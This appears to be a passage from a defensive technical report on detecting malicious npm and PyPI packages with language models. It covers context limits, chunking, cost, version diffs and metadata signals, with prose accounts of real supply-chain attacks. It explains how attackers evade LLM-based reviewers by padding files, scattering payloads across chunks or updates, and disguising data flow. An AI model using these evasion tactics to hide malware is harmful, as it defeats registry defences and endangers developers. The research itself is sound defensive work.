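Windows may well reach that size. But an attacker can make a file longer with almost no effort, whereas a longer window takes engineering and computing power. A larger window would solve the problem only if it were larger than anything the registry accepts. Nguyen and colleagues also point out that processing the largest packages whole would take too much memory and time for a system that monitors a registry as new versions appear.

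An agent would not use all of a larger window for code either, since its searches and earlier messages take up part of it.

### What tests of long inputs measure

Researchers have known for some years that a model can receive text and still fail to use it. *Lost in the Middle* (2023) reported that models use information at the beginning and end of a long input better than information in the middle. According to Mercury's summary, Chroma's *Context Rot* (2025) reported that models become less reliable as their input gets longer.

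The needle-in-a-haystack test is a common way to study how well models use long contexts. The tester hides a fact in a long stretch of irrelevant text, asks the model for it, and repeats the test with different lengths and positions. A high score shows that a model can retrieve something when the question describes what to look for. A code reviewer has a harder job because it doesn't know what the payload looks like, or whether there is one, and the evidence may be several ordinary-looking lines that are suspicious only together. So a model may do very well on the needle test and still review long files poorly.

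Sovrano, Bauer and Bacchelli (2025) adapted the test to code in *Large Language Models for In-File Vulnerability Localization*. They looked for vulnerabilities rather than malware, and chose three common kinds that arise when a program uses what a user types without checking it. In cross-site scripting, a web page runs an attacker's code in another user's browser. In SQL injection, the input changes a database command, and in path traversal, it gives an attacker access to files that should be off limits.

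One study first tested whether six models could name the faulty line in 794 real files, each containing one known flaw. The models did poorly even though the files were short. The median file for cross-site scripting had 8,654 characters, less than 2% of what GPT-4o could take in, yet GPT-4o located only 31% of those flaws. It found 51% of the SQL injections and 57% of the path traversals. For every type of flaw, the models were less likely to find it when the file was longer or the flaw was further down.

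In real files, the flaw's position is correlated with file length, and long files may differ from short ones in other ways. The second experiment therefore held the flaw constant. For each of 15 flaws, Sovrano and colleagues put the faulty line in a function of up to about 500 characters. They then placed this function at different positions in files of 4,000, 8,000, 16,000 and 25,000 characters, filling the rest with other code from the same file or repository. They ran each model five times on each of the 530 combinations of file and position for each type of flaw.

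Detection again fell with file length, and it fell more steeply with position in the file. In the largest files, the models concentrated on the beginning and neglected the end, where *Lost in the Middle* would predict a recovery. Sovrano and colleagues call this "lost in the end". When the models named a wrong line in a long file, it tended to be within the first 6,000 characters.

These files were small compared with the windows of GPT-4 and GPT-4o. By the usual rule of four characters per token, 25,000 characters is about 6,000 tokens, or 5% of those windows. For SQL injection, the three most accurate models began to have difficulty above 4,000 characters, or about 1,000 tokens. The pattern appeared in all six models, whose windows ranged from 8,000 to 128,000 tokens, so a larger window did not prevent it on this task.

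Sovrano and colleagues suggest that models neglect the end of a file because they learnt in training that flaws come early. In the researchers' collection of real files, most flaws are within the first 10,000 characters, and the models' wrong guesses in the longest test files have a similar distribution. If the models trained on files like these, they may have learnt this pattern. The explanation is plausible, but the experiment doesn't test it. The prompt also always placed the instructions before the code, so the results can't show whether models missed late flaws because they were near the end of the file or because they were far from the instructions.

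The scoring may exaggerate the decline, too. A model got credit only for naming a line that the official fix had changed. If it instead reported another genuine flaw in the padding, that counted as a miss, and longer files have more room for such flaws.

The same researchers also cut the real files into pieces and asked about each piece separately. GPT-4 then found 40% of the cross-site scripting flaws instead of 24%. This fits with dilution, since the model and the code were the same and only the amount of surrounding text had changed. But asking about every piece also gives the model many more guesses than asking once per file, so dilution may not explain the whole gain.

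### How much of this remains in 2026

All six models in that study date from May 2024 or earlier, so its thresholds are not a reliable guide to current ones. Malware may also be easier to detect than vulnerabilities. A vulnerability is often a missing check, which leaves no code to notice, whereas a payload has to do something, such as read a password file or contact a server.

More recent figures suggest that performance now starts to decline at much greater lengths. The earlier estimate of d for GPT-5 nano, based on results from Noirot Ferrand and colleagues, was about 0.91 on the large files it read and 0.95 on smaller ones. The large files ranged from 25,000 to about 250,000 tokens, so even the shortest was four times as long as the longest file in Sovrano's experiment. The four-point loss is small. It depends on an assumption about which files went unread, but even a loss twice as large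 would not resemble the collapse of 2024.

The evidence is less encouraging for inputs of several hundred thousand tokens or more. In Cloudflare's test from April 2026, models failed to flag most large scripts even when their context windows could hold much of each one. The Luna comparison above points the same way. Neither test put the same payload in files of different lengths, as Sovrano and colleagues did, so the large files may have been harder to judge for some reason other than their length.

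Models may also get better at handling long inputs. When Sovrano and colleagues gave the models short pieces, the open models caught up with the commercial ones and sometimes beat them. The researchers infer that the commercial models' main advantage may have been better handling of long inputs. If so, developers can improve this ability, and d on long inputs should rise as they do. It may not rise as fast as context windows grow, though, because a developer can offer a million-token window before the model can use all of it equally well.

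Mercury's engineers also expected more tokens to give worse results, so they pruned the code before scanning it. In the scan that the company described in July 2026, they gave the model one file of gathered code for each web route (the code that handles one kind of request), after removing functions for logging, metrics and similar tasks. The median pruned file had 18,572 tokens and the 99th percentile was 214,297, and every file could fit in a million-token window. Mercury reports that most of the false alarms its engineers reviewed came from poor reasoning or from misunderstanding the company's business, and few from missing code. This supports the view that d becomes the bottleneck once c is high. However, the company did not publish a count of the flaws that the model missed, or compare results with and without the pruning.

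### Comparing models with different windows

The most direct published comparison of window size with accuracy seems to show that the window hardly matters. Ryan and colleagues evaluated 13 models in a paper first released in February 2026 as *Mind the Gap*. They concluded in that version that window size had negligible power to explain accuracy. In the current version, they identify package length as the only one of five factors with a meaningful association.

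Their numbers are less clear than this. The February analysis gives a rank correlation of 0.52 between window size and performance, described there as moderate, with a p-value of 0.07. With only 13 models, a correlation has to reach about 0.56 to be statistically significant, so the study could easily miss a real effect of moderate size. The data are compatible with anything from no relation to a very strong one.

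That correlation also concerns a different task, in which the model names the specific signs of malice in a package already known to be malicious. For plain detection, the rank correlation between context window and average score across the 13 models in the current version is about 0.4, again too weak to be significant with so few models.

The larger difficulty is that the packages were small. The full collection has 370 malicious and 3,700 harmless packages, but the detection test used only one file from each of 10 malicious and 93 harmless packages. The longest harmless package had 260 lines. Even at 20 tokens a line, that is about 5,200 tokens, or about a third of the smallest context window in the study (16,000 tokens, for Microsoft's Phi-4) and half a percent of the largest.

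A window can affect c only when the code might not fit, and in this study the code fit easily in every window. The study therefore can't show whether larger windows help with large packages. It does show that models with the same window can differ widely. Seven of the 13 models have windows of 128,000 tokens, and their average detection scores range from 0.40 to 0.70, where 1 is perfect. Anyone choosing a model for its window should first test how well it recognises malware in short files.

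A small context window can also make a model's accuracy look better than it is. Of the six models Sovrano and colleagues tested, Llama 3 had the smallest window, yet it located 48% of the SQL injections, slightly more than GPT-4, whose window was 16 times as large. But Llama 3's score covers 257 files and GPT-4's covers 292, presumably because the other 35 were too long for Llama 3. The small window kept the most difficult files out of the score. A reviewer that reports accuracy only on the files it read will look better for the same reason.

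### What long inputs cost

The price of a single call's input rises in proportion to its length. Noirot Ferrand and colleagues note that some providers charge a higher rate for very long prompts, which makes the price rise faster. At a flat rate, a million-token file would cost five times as much as a 200,000-token file. If the provider doubled its rate above 200,000 tokens, the larger file would cost ten times as much if the higher rate applied to the whole prompt, or nine times as much if it applied only to the excess.

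With a cheap model, the cost is still modest. Filling a million-token window costs 20 cents at Luna's rate. The first wave of the Shai-Hulud attack, in September 2025, reached more than 1,150 packages. If each had contained a million tokens of code, reading all of it once would have cost about $230 before any surcharge. Reading harmless code costs more, because a reviewer that reads every large payload in full must also read every large bundle that honest developers publish, each time a new version appears. More capable models, which an operator would want for the hardest files, also cost more per token.

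Input is only part of the cost of a scan. Mercury paid $178.90 to scan more than 1,200 routes with GPT-5, about 15 cents per route, and more than half of the total was for the model's output.

When an agent reviews code, the number of tokens processed grows much faster than the amount of code it reads. Each time the agent asks for another file, the model processes the whole conversation again with the new file added. An agent that reads 200,000 tokens of code in 20 steps of 10,000 processes 10,000 tokens at the first step, 20,000 at the second and so on, for a total of 2.1 million. Filling a million-token window in 100 such steps brings the total to 50.5 million, about 24 times as many tokens for five times as much code. Providers charge less for the repeated part of a conversation, so the bill grows more slowly than the token count, but an operator who gives an agent a larger window may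 still want to limit how much of it the agent can fill.

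## Can the code be read in batches?

A reviewer can split the code into chunks that fit its context window. If it reads every chunk, the payload always reaches the model, so c is 1 however large the package is. Detection then depends on how well the model judges each chunk and how the software combines the answers.

### How BewAIre splits a large change

Datadog first built BewAIre to review pull requests, which are proposed changes to a codebase. The company gets nearly 10,000 of them a week. For each one, the model receives the diff, which lists the lines added and removed, along with facts such as who wrote the change.

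Lamb, Hamsen and colleagues explain in *Detecting malicious pull requests at scale with LLMs* how the first version of BewAIre, from 2025, handled a diff that was too large. The software split the diff repeatedly until every chunk was small enough. It cut just before the marker for the next file where possible, otherwise at a line break, and as a last resort in the middle of the text. The model judged the chunks one after another, and the whole change received the most severe verdict. If one of seven chunks looked malicious and the rest looked harmless, BewAIre reported the change as malicious and gave the model's reasons.

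Repeated splitting can produce many chunks. Ten rounds of halving give 1,024, which would take almost three hours to judge in sequence at ten seconds per call. Datadog therefore limited the depth of the splitting and the number of chunks. Lamb and colleagues don't say what happened to text beyond those limits. With any such limit, code above a certain size can still go unread, so the software should at least record when it reaches the limit.

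Lamb and colleagues report that BewAIre was more than 99.3% accurate on a test set of several hundred changes. But when most changes are harmless, a reviewer can miss a lot of malware and still have high accuracy. They therefore also report the balanced accuracy, the average of the share of malicious changes detected and the share of harmless changes cleared, which was above 93.5%. If BewAIre cleared nearly all the harmless changes, it may have missed up to 13% of the malicious ones.

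### A cheap screen and an expensive investigation

In the 2026 version, a cheap model screens every change and an agent investigates what it flags. The agent can look up information missing from the diff, such as the author's history or an earlier commit that someone reverted to keep it out of the final diff. In one real attack, the cheap model flagged a command hidden in a file name, and the agent found that the author's account was seven days old and had no followers.

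According to Doutre and colleagues, the second stage raised accuracy on 690 test diffs from 97.4% to 99.86% and cut false positives from 17 to 0. Total errors therefore fell from 18 to one, which means one malicious change was missed both before and after the agent was added. This fits the design, since the agent reviews only flagged changes.

Datadog therefore set the cheap model to flag changes more readily and added ordinary code to support it. The model had been accepting web addresses that imitated Datadog's own, so this code now checks the addresses in a change against a list of known lookalikes.

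Doutre and colleagues also estimated what the two stages would cost for npm packages:

| Package size | Screening | Agent, when it runs | Average per package |
|---|---|---|---|
| 5,000 tokens (median) | $0.016 | $0.17 | $0.025 |
| 87,000 tokens (90th percentile) | $0.038 | $0.686 | $0.072 |

The averages assume that the agent investigates 5% of packages, whatever their size. Datadog reported all these figures itself. It also assembled the test data, ran the tests and offers the scanner to its customers.

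### False alarms add up

When one malicious chunk is enough to condemn a package, every extra chunk is another opportunity for a mistake. If the model wrongly flags a harmless chunk with probability f, and its errors are independent, the chance of at least one false alarm in n harmless chunks is

1 − (1 − f)ⁿ

| Harmless chunks | f = 0.5% | f = 0.03% |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 0.5% | 0.03% |
| 10 | 4.9% | 0.3% |
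| 100 | 39% | 3% |
| 1,000 | 99% | 26% |

An error rate of 0.5% would be excellent for a single verdict, but at that rate per chunk, a review split into 100 chunks flags 39% of harmless packages. Lamb and colleagues report a 0.5% rate for BewAIre, though for whole changes rather than chunks. They needed six months of work on prompts and data to reduce it from over 10%.

Errors within one package are unlikely to be independent, because a model that mistakes a company's obfuscation for malware in one chunk will probably do so again in the next. The false alarms then concentrate in fewer packages, so the share of packages flagged will be at least 0.5% but below 39%.

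Many older scanners based on fixed rules flag a package if any one rule matches, which can produce many false alarms. In *Cutting the Gordian Knot*, Guo, Liu and colleagues (2026) ran four such tools on about 9,600 harmless PyPI packages, most of them popular. One tool flagged 88% of the packages and another 85%, while the most selective, GuardDog, flagged about 5%. GuardDog combined results in the same way as the others, but its individual checks misfired far less often.

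A stricter threshold for each piece can reduce false alarms. Nguyen and colleagues tested several thresholds with a model that scored extracts of related code, judging each package by its highest score. At a threshold of 0.7, only 64% of the packages they flagged were malicious. At 0.8, 96% were, but at 0.9 the model missed more of the malware.

A better model helps too. Noirot Ferrand and colleagues tested a fallback for files that were still too large after preprocessing. It scored the three most suspicious pieces of each file separately and used the highest score. With GPT-5 nano and a single call per piece, false alarms on 346 large harmless files rose from 4 to 10. With GPT-5.6 Luna there were none. Some of the increase with GPT-5 nano came from reading more files. Three pieces are far fewer than 100, so we can't tell from this test how Luna would do on a very large package.

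Another option is to flag a package only when at least two chunks look suspicious. In the example with 100 chunks, that would cut the false-alarm rate from 39% to 9%. But it would also miss any payload that fits in one chunk, and so many attacks put the payload in a single file that the reduction in false alarms isn't worth it.

BewAIre's second stage is a better answer, because the agent can dismiss a false alarm before it reaches a person. But each dismissal costs money, and the agent is by far the more expensive stage. If false alarms accumulate this way, the estimate that 5% of packages need an investigation can't hold for very large packages. At an error rate of 0.5% per chunk, a harmless package with 100 chunks would trigger the agent up to 39% of the time.

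### When the behaviour is split between chunks

Splitting can also separate the code that reads a password from the code that sends it away. Many harmless programs do one or the other, so neither chunk gets a severe verdict, and taking the most severe verdict across chunks doesn't help.

When Nguyen and colleagues gave a model all the code in 500-token chunks as a baseline, it detected only 55.5% of the malicious packages. The same model detected 72.9% when it received extracts of related code, so the way the code was split probably caused some of the misses. Others occurred because the model was small and is now old. Chunks of 500 tokens are also very short, and larger ones would separate fewer related lines.

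An attacker can scatter a payload on purpose. Wyss, Tassio and colleagues tested this in *Evaluating LLM-Based Detection of Malicious Package Updates in npm* by mixing the statements of two known types of attack with harmless code across large updates. GPT-4-Turbo and Gemini 2.0 Flash both missed the attacks, even though each update fit in one call. GPT-4o missed them only when the researchers also disguised how data moved through the code. Chunking would remove GPT-4o's advantage if it put the statements in different calls.

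Missing context can also cause false alarms. Madugula's *Finding Vulnerabilities at Scale* describes a system at the security company SonicWall that looks for accidental flaws in C code, starting with one file at a time. In a constructed example, three models all report that a function could write past the end of the memory reserved for its output, because one input character can become seven. An agent with access to the whole codebase then finds that all 11 places that call the function reserve nine times the length of the input, so the overflow can't occur in practice. Like BewAIre's agent, this agent can correct a false alarm but can't recover a flaw that the models didn't flag.

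### Overlap, notes and a joining pass

One remedy is to overlap neighbouring chunks. If each chunk repeats the last 20,000 tokens of the one before, any stretch of code up to that length will appear whole in at least one chunk. With chunks of 200,000 tokens, this adds about 11% to the text the model reads. Overlap works well for a function that straddles a boundary, but it doesn't help with two related functions in files that are far apart, and an attacker can choose how far apart to put them.

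Zhao and colleagues group code by content instead of position. After extracting the code around sensitive operations, they merge two extracts if the lines they share make up more than 30% of all the lines in either. In their example, this groups the code that steals browser cookies with two requests that send the cookies out. The method depends on having extracted the relevant code.

Another approach is for the model to keep running notes on what it has learnt and receive them with each new chunk. This can connect distant pieces of code, but the model has to record the first piece before it knows why that piece matters. The summaries that agents make in long sessions have the same weakness. The reviewer also has to process the chunks in order, so it can't save time by running many calls at once.

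A final joining pass avoids the problem of order. One call per chunk produces a report, and a last call reads all the reports together. Xu, Zhu and colleagues (2025), in *When Does Divide and Conquer Work for Long Context LLM?*, analyse this design and identify three ways in which it can lose information:

- The reports may leave out something that the final answer needs, because it depends on several chunks at once.
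- The model may misread an individual chunk, which happens more often as chunks get longer.
- The last call may combine good reports badly.

Their model of the system multiplies together the shares of performance that remain after each of these losses. If 90% remains after each of the three, the system performs at 73% of the ideal.

The result therefore depends heavily on what the reviewer asks for in each report. Xu and colleagues use the example of finding the second-smallest number in a long list. Reporting only the second-smallest number in each chunk can give the wrong answer, but reporting the two smallest always includes the right one. A malware reviewer has the same problem if each report contains only "benign" or "malicious". It would be better for the model to list every place where a chunk reads sensitive data, contacts a server, runs a command or decodes hidden text, even if the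 code looks harmless. In the last call, the model could then look for connections between these places.

The reports must together fit in one window. With 79 chunks and 1,000 tokens per report, the last call reads 79,000 tokens, which is manageable. If the reviewer instead split the same code into 500-token chunks, it would need more than 31,000 reports, which would overflow a million-token window even at 50 tokens each.

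In tests on retrieval, question answering and summarisation, Xu and colleagues found that weaker models reading a long text in chunks could beat GPT-4o reading it whole. They also argue that when a task depends heavily on connections between chunks, better models can't make up for what is lost in splitting. Their results support the design of the joining pass, but the tests included no malware, so they don't show how many split payloads it would catch.

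### What it costs to read everything

The largest package in Nguyen and colleagues' dataset has 15.8 million tokens, so it needs at least 79 chunks of 200,000 tokens. Reading it once costs about $3.16 at $0.20 per million input tokens, or $63 at $4. Overlapping the chunks by 20,000 tokens raises their number to 88 and the cost to about $3.50 or $70. The actual number of chunks would be slightly higher because each call also needs room for the instructions.

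Small chunks cost more because every call repeats the instructions and produces an answer. A straight line through Datadog's two screening estimates suggests a fixed cost of about 1.5 cents per call. At that rate, 79 calls add just over a dollar. With chunks of 500 tokens, the same package would need about 31,500 calls, and the fixed costs would come to around $460.

A few dollars is affordable for one suspicious package, but the cost adds up across a registry. Wyss and colleagues cite an estimate of 674,300 npm updates a month and report an average of 546,363 tokens per package in their samples. If that average held for all updates, reading each package in full would cost about $74,000 a month at $0.20 per million tokens and nearly $1.5 million at $4. Their samples include many popular packages, so the average may be too high for npm as a whole. Most of this money would be spent rereading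 code that the reviewer had already read in an earlier version.

### Reading only what is new

The simplest way to reduce repeated review is to store each verdict with a hash of the file or package, a short fingerprint that in practice changes whenever the contents change. If the same hash appears again, the reviewer can reuse the verdict. Datadog does this for whole packages. Noirot Ferrand and colleagues propose doing it for individual modules inside a bundle, so a library bundled by thousands of developers would need only one review.

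An attacker can't reuse a cleared file's verdict for altered code, because changing even one character produces a new hash and a new review. But a wrong verdict persists until someone deletes it, so an operator should discard old verdicts after switching to a better model. A file that was harmless in one package may also play a part in an attack in another, if a new file calls it with stolen data.

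A reviewer can save more by comparing each new version with the one before and reading only the differences. Datadog added this to BewAIre for package upgrades. Wyss and colleagues, whose paper appeared at the RAID security conference in 2025, provide the most detailed test. An ordinary diff often lists far more than has really changed, since renaming one variable can alter hundreds of lines. They therefore built a "smart-diff" in three steps:

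1. They run every JavaScript file in both versions through a tool that compresses code and another that expands it again. This removes comments and makes names and layout uniform.
2. For files present in both versions, they use a plagiarism detector to find long matching sequences and remove code that has merely moved or changed its variable names.
3. They run an ordinary diff on what is left and send the result to the model.

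The next table shows how much this reduced the input. The last column refers to the 128,000-token window of the GPT-4 models they tested.

| Input | Average tokens | Too large for the window |
|---|---|---|
| Whole package | 546,363 | 16.86% |
| Ordinary diff | 115,895 | 7.18% |
| Smart-diff | 25,246 | 1.47% |

The smart-diff cut the average input by 95.4%. Reading all of npm's updates would then cost about $3,400 a month instead of $74,000, assuming the average size in the table and a price of $0.20 per million tokens.

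All three models caught all 209 malicious samples. Out of 2,000 ordinary updates, GPT-4o wrongly flagged 8, GPT-4-Turbo 16 and Gemini 2.0 Flash 75. But the malicious samples were less varied than their number suggests, because 163 were altered copies of well-known packages, apparently from one campaign, with similar scripts for mining cryptocurrency. The other 46 were real malicious updates. Even with all 46 caught, the true miss rate for such updates could be as high as about 6%, and the models' training data may have included descriptions of some of these well-known attacks.

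Wyss and colleagues also ran the system for nearly three months on live updates to packages with more than 100,000 downloads a week. Of 29,880 updates, they skipped the 71.7% that changed no code or scripts and the 2.6% whose smart-diffs were too large for the context window. That 2.6% comes to about 780 updates, or roughly one in eleven of those that changed code or scripts. GPT-4o flagged seven of the 7,661 updates it read. Three were false alarms, and the other four were versions of a heavily obfuscated video downloader in which the researchers found nothing clearly malicious.

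In the attack on ai-sdk-ollama, comparing versions would have removed the unchanged library code and left little besides the two files that the attacker added. But one of those files was the 4.5 MB payload, so a reviewer that skipped oversized diffs, as Wyss and colleagues did in the live run, would have skipped this update. A reviewer that compares versions may therefore still need to read the changes in chunks.

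### When the earlier version was not clean

Reading only the changes is safe if the earlier version was harmless. Wyss and colleagues explicitly assume that the attacker takes over a package that was benign at first. Many attackers instead publish a new package that is malicious from the start, so there is no earlier version to compare it with. The researchers identified the original of each of the 163 altered copies by hand. An automated reviewer would have to find the original on its own or read the whole package.

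If a review misses a payload, later reviews that cover only the diffs can't catch it unless the payload changes, because a diff leaves out code that is the same in the old and new versions. Reviewing the whole package again with a better model gives another chance to catch it.

A reviewer should compare a new version with the last one it has read and cleared, even if others have appeared since. If a reviewer had compared each of the four malicious versions of ai-sdk-ollama with the version published just before it, up to three of the comparisons could have started from a malicious version. The payload would probably still have shown up as new code because its encoding changed between versions, but an unchanged copy would not have appeared in the diff.

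An attacker can also spread a payload over several updates so that each diff looks harmless. This is the split-chunk problem again, except that the pieces are separated by time. A reviewer can reduce the risk by giving the model both the new lines and the unchanged code they call. The model also needs to read the whole package at the first review and periodically after that, which offsets some of the reading saved by comparing versions.

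## What can be learnt from metadata before reading code?

Reading in batches and comparing versions both use tokens before the reviewer has any idea where a payload might be. Metadata takes far fewer tokens to read, often only a few hundred. The registry publishes facts about every release, and ordinary software can list a package's files and check their types almost instantly.

### The llm-oracle package

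The npm package llm-oracle was aimed at programmers who build applications on language models. SafeDep's *Malicious Open Source Library Analysis* describes how the security company took it apart by hand, starting with a list of its six files and a check of their types:

| File | Bytes | Type |
|---|---|---|
| Base64Decode.ts | 16,773,255 | Windows program |
| README.md | 3,105 | Text |
| index.js | 2,665 | Text |
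| package.json | 2,170 | JSON data |
| LICENSE | 1,111 | Text |
| HISTORY.md | 252 | Text |

The .ts extension is for TypeScript, a language closely related to JavaScript, so the largest file's name suggests that it is source code for decoding text. A file-type check, which examines a file's contents instead of its name, identified it as a Windows program. An honest developer has little reason to disguise a program as source code, so this one line of output is strong evidence of malice.

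The other five files total 9,303 bytes, or about 2,300 tokens, so a model can easily read them all. The code in index.js waits a minute, copies the disguised program to another folder under the name chrome.exe, and launches it with a request for administrator rights.

A reviewer can reject the package without unpacking or reading the program. At four characters per token, the program would come to more than four million tokens, and a model would learn little from reading them. SafeDep had to unpack the file, decompile part of it and decode another layer to reach a script that looks for cryptocurrency wallets and records keystrokes.

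SafeDep's analysts already knew that another company had reported llm-oracle as malicious. Their own scanner, which relied by default on another project's data, had not flagged it. The case therefore doesn't show that a routine scan would have caught the package. However, a file-type check takes little enough computing to run on every file in a registry.

### What a reviewer can obtain cheaply

| Item | What it can reveal | Where it comes from |
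|---|---|---|
| Manifest | Install scripts, entry points, dependencies | Publisher |
| Name, description, homepage, contact address | Imitation of a well-known package | Publisher |
| File list, sizes and true types | Unexpected or oversized files, false file endings | Calculated from the package |
| Publisher and version history | A changed account or address, releases in quick succession | Registry |
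| Comparison with the source repository | Files with no public source | Calculated from both |

An attacker can write almost anything in the fields that a publisher controls, but data that the registry records or ordinary software calculates is harder to falsify.

Many attacks begin in the manifest, so it is a good place to start. Of the 6,420 malicious npm packages that Guo and colleagues studied, 72% launched their attack through an install script. In 21%, they found no malicious JavaScript, only a malicious command in the manifest, which a reviewer that reads only source files would miss.

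Install scripts are also rare among npm packages. Guo and colleagues cite an earlier finding that only 2.2% of packages declare one, while about 82% of the malicious packages they studied do. Suppose that one new package in 1,000 is malicious. Out of 100,000 packages, about 82 malicious ones and 2,200 harmless ones would then have an install script. Finding a script would therefore raise the chance that a package is malicious from 0.1% to about 3.6%, which justifies reading it next but not rejecting it. Legitimate tools such as husky and prisma also use install scripts.

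The reviewer also needs the right copy of the manifest. When someone publishes an npm package, the registry receives one manifest separately from the package and another inside it. According to Lutra Security's *Manifest confusion*, npm never fully checks that the two agree, and harmless differences between them are very common. Sonatype's *npm Manifest Confusion* describes a test package whose internal manifest listed an install script and a dependency that did not appear on the npm website. npm later began to block packages whose two manifests give different names or version numbers, according to GitHub's *Block npm package publishes when names and versions don’t match* (2023). GitHub left other mismatches for further study, so a reviewer should still read the manifest inside the package.

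### Publisher, history and source repository

Metadata can reveal an attack that isn't visible in the package's own code. On March 31, 2026, an attacker took over the npm account of a maintainer of axios, a JavaScript library with more than 100 million downloads a week. In *Compromised axios npm package delivers cross-platform RAT*, Tafani-Dereeper (2026) compared the malicious version 1.14.1 with the clean release before it. The source code was identical, and the only meaningful change in the manifest was a new dependency, plain-crypto-js, which no axios code imported. The dependency's install script downloaded a program that gave the attacker remote control of the machine.

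The registry's records also showed that an automated workflow on GitHub had published the clean version through npm's trusted publishing, which links a package to an approved workflow. The malicious version came directly from the maintainer's account, which now had a different email address. SafeDep's *axios Compromised* adds that the axios repository had no tag, or version label, for 1.14.1. In *Supply Chain Attack on Axios Pulls Malicious Dependency from npm* (2026), software developer Simon Willison considers a registry release without a matching GitHub release a useful warning sign.

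These signals depend on what is normal for the package. The attacker also published axios 0.30.4, in an older series that had not yet moved to trusted publishing, so the lack of a trusted publisher would not have been a change from earlier releases in that series.

Release timing can also help. *Practical Automated Detection of Malicious npm Packages* (2022) describes a detector that uses the time since the previous version and the type of update (major, minor or patch), along with changes in the code. Four releases in 17 seconds, as in the attack on ai-sdk-ollama, would stand out.

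A reviewer can also compare the package with its public source code. *SoK* (2025), a paper on whether packages can be reproduced from their source, defines a phantom file as one whose hash matches no file in the repository. Most phantom files are probably harmless. In the npm updates examined in *Are your dependencies code reviewed?* (2022), 89.4% of phantom files were JavaScript or related files, many of which a build tool may have generated from source in another language. The 2022 paper therefore recommends particular attention when a new version contains phantom files and the current one does not.

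Phantom files can also reveal that a package falsely links to somebody else's repository. *SoK* describes a test on about 14,000 Python packages, where comparing packages with the wrong repository produced significantly more phantom files than comparing them with the right one. But the check needs a repository and a known version. *Software Supply Chain Smells* (2026) lists a missing source address and a missing release tag as warning signs, partly because a reviewer can't make the comparison without both.

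### File maps

Once a reviewer decides to read a package, it can use a file map, such as the codemap that Datadog gives its agent, to choose which lines to request first. The map's length depends on how many files and named items it lists, not on how much code they contain. At 20 tokens per entry, a map of 500 files and 2,000 functions takes 50,000 tokens.

Doutre and colleagues compared four ways of giving a package to the agent that investigates what BewAIre's cheaper model has flagged. They ran all four on Datadog's collection of malicious packages:

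| What the agent receives | End-to-end accuracy |
|---|---|
| The whole package, with an error if it is too large | 94.1% |
| Chunks made with the first stage's splitting code | 93.7% |
| Chunks based on the agent's own context window | 94.9% |
| A file map and a tool for reading lines | 95.2% |

End-to-end accuracy here is the share of correct verdicts multiplied by the share of runs that finish without an error. A system with 95% correct verdicts and 4% of runs ending in an error would score 0.95 × 0.96, or 91.2%. Frequent failures on large packages therefore lower a reviewer's score even if its verdicts are usually correct.

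The map scored highest, but the differences are small, and Datadog doesn't give the number of packages. If there were 1,000, the map and the baseline would differ by 11 packages. Two independent samples would need about 3,200 packages each for the same percentage difference to be statistically significant, though a comparison on the same packages might need fewer.

The averages are also weak evidence about large packages, which are the reason for having a map. Doutre and colleagues report that the map eliminated runtime errors, so its 95.2% should be its share of correct verdicts. They also report that this share matched the best of the other methods. If so, no more than about 1.2% of the baseline's runs can have failed, even though they describe the baseline's error rate on large packages as significant, so oversized packages were probably a small part of the collection.

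The comparison also doesn't include harmless packages, so it can't show whether the map causes fewer false alarms than chunking. The agent with the map received the first model's verdict as well, so it didn't have to find the payload from the outline alone. The clearer advantage may be cost, which Doutre and colleagues say fell drastically, but they publish no figures for each method.

A map shows where code is but not what it does. A function called sendReport might send a crash report to the developer or a password to an attacker, and the agent has to read it to find out. Obfuscation makes the map less informative, because names such as "_0x50e6" are meaningless. For ai-sdk-ollama, a map would show a 4.5 MB file with very few named functions, which is suspicious, but it would not show what the numbers in the file decode to. Some build tools put an entire program on one line, so an agent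 that can request code only by line number can't select a part of it.

### Metadata that the attacker writes

*Tactics, Techniques, and Procedures (TTPs) in Interpreted Malware* (Zhang, Zhou and colleagues, 2024) describes GENTTP, an early system that treats deceptive metadata and malicious code as separate parts of an attack. GENTTP uses a language model to analyse PyPI packages already known to be malicious. The model identifies how a package tricks people into installing it from six metadata fields (name, version, description, homepage, contact and dependencies), and what happens when the package runs from its code. One package, Ascii2text, copied its description from the popular `art` package, while its code downloaded and ran a script that searched for passwords.

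With GPT-4, GENTTP identified on average 90% of the attack techniques that security reports had listed for 365 packages. Zhang and colleagues also looked for failures in a larger set of 3,735 packages. They found 32 without metadata, so the model could not infer the deception, and 65 without code. Another 54 had more than 15,000 lines, because the attacker had copied an existing project or added malicious code to one, and GENTTP could fail to identify what that code did. It also could not analyse compiled programs like the one in llm-oracle. Because every package was known to be malicious, the tests don't show how often GENTTP would wrongly infer deception from a harmless package's metadata.

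Careless attackers leave traces in these fields. In the dataset behind *A Machine Learning-Based Approach For Detecting Malicious PyPI Packages* (2024), 20% of malicious packages had a valid homepage or repository, while 73% of benign packages had a valid homepage. Author email addresses were valid for 46% of malicious packages and 87% of benign ones. But a careful attacker can easily fill in both fields. *A Large-scale Fine-grained Analysis of Packages in Open-Source Software Ecosystems* (2024) found similar patterns, including shorter descriptions and fewer authors, but advises against relying on them heavily because they are easy to fake. *CHASE* (2026), a paper on using LLM agents to analyse malicious packages, warns that language models can now write plausible metadata, which makes these signs of carelessness less useful.

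An attacker who takes over a trusted package inherits its good record. In May 2026, attackers compromised several packages from TanStack, a family of JavaScript libraries. According to Tenable's *CVE 2026 45321*, they published through the project's own trusted-publisher identity, without changing the publishing workflow. The malicious versions also carried valid provenance, a signed record of the pipeline that built them, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Mini Shai-Hulud Hits TanStack npm Packages*. A publisher check that would have caught axios 1.14.1 would have passed these releases.

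Other metadata still revealed the attack. In *TanStack npm Packages Compromised*, Kurmi (2026) reports that each compromised package had an altered manifest and an unexpected file of about 2.3 MB in its top folder. The manifest had a new optional dependency that fetched code from a copy of the project's repository and ran it during installation. Kurmi's company, StepSecurity, flagged one release within minutes, partly because of the extra file and the way the manifest fetched code. A reviewer that relaxed its checks for publishers with a good history would have lost this chance to catch the attack.

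### Deciding what to read first

Guo and colleagues' results show how well metadata can rank packages. One tool they tested, EMPHunter, uses only install scripts, grouping similar ones and ranking the unusual ones first. The researchers mixed one malicious package at a time with 111 harmless ones. The malicious package ranked first in 49% of trials and in the top ten in 80%. A reviewer that could read only the top ten of the 112 packages would therefore find the malicious one about four times out of five.

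Using the same ranking to clear packages would be dangerous. The trials covered only the 5,236 malicious packages that declare an install script, not the other 1,184. A reviewer that treated every package outside the top ten as harmless would miss about 1,020 of the packages with install scripts and all of those without, or 34% of the malicious packages in the study.

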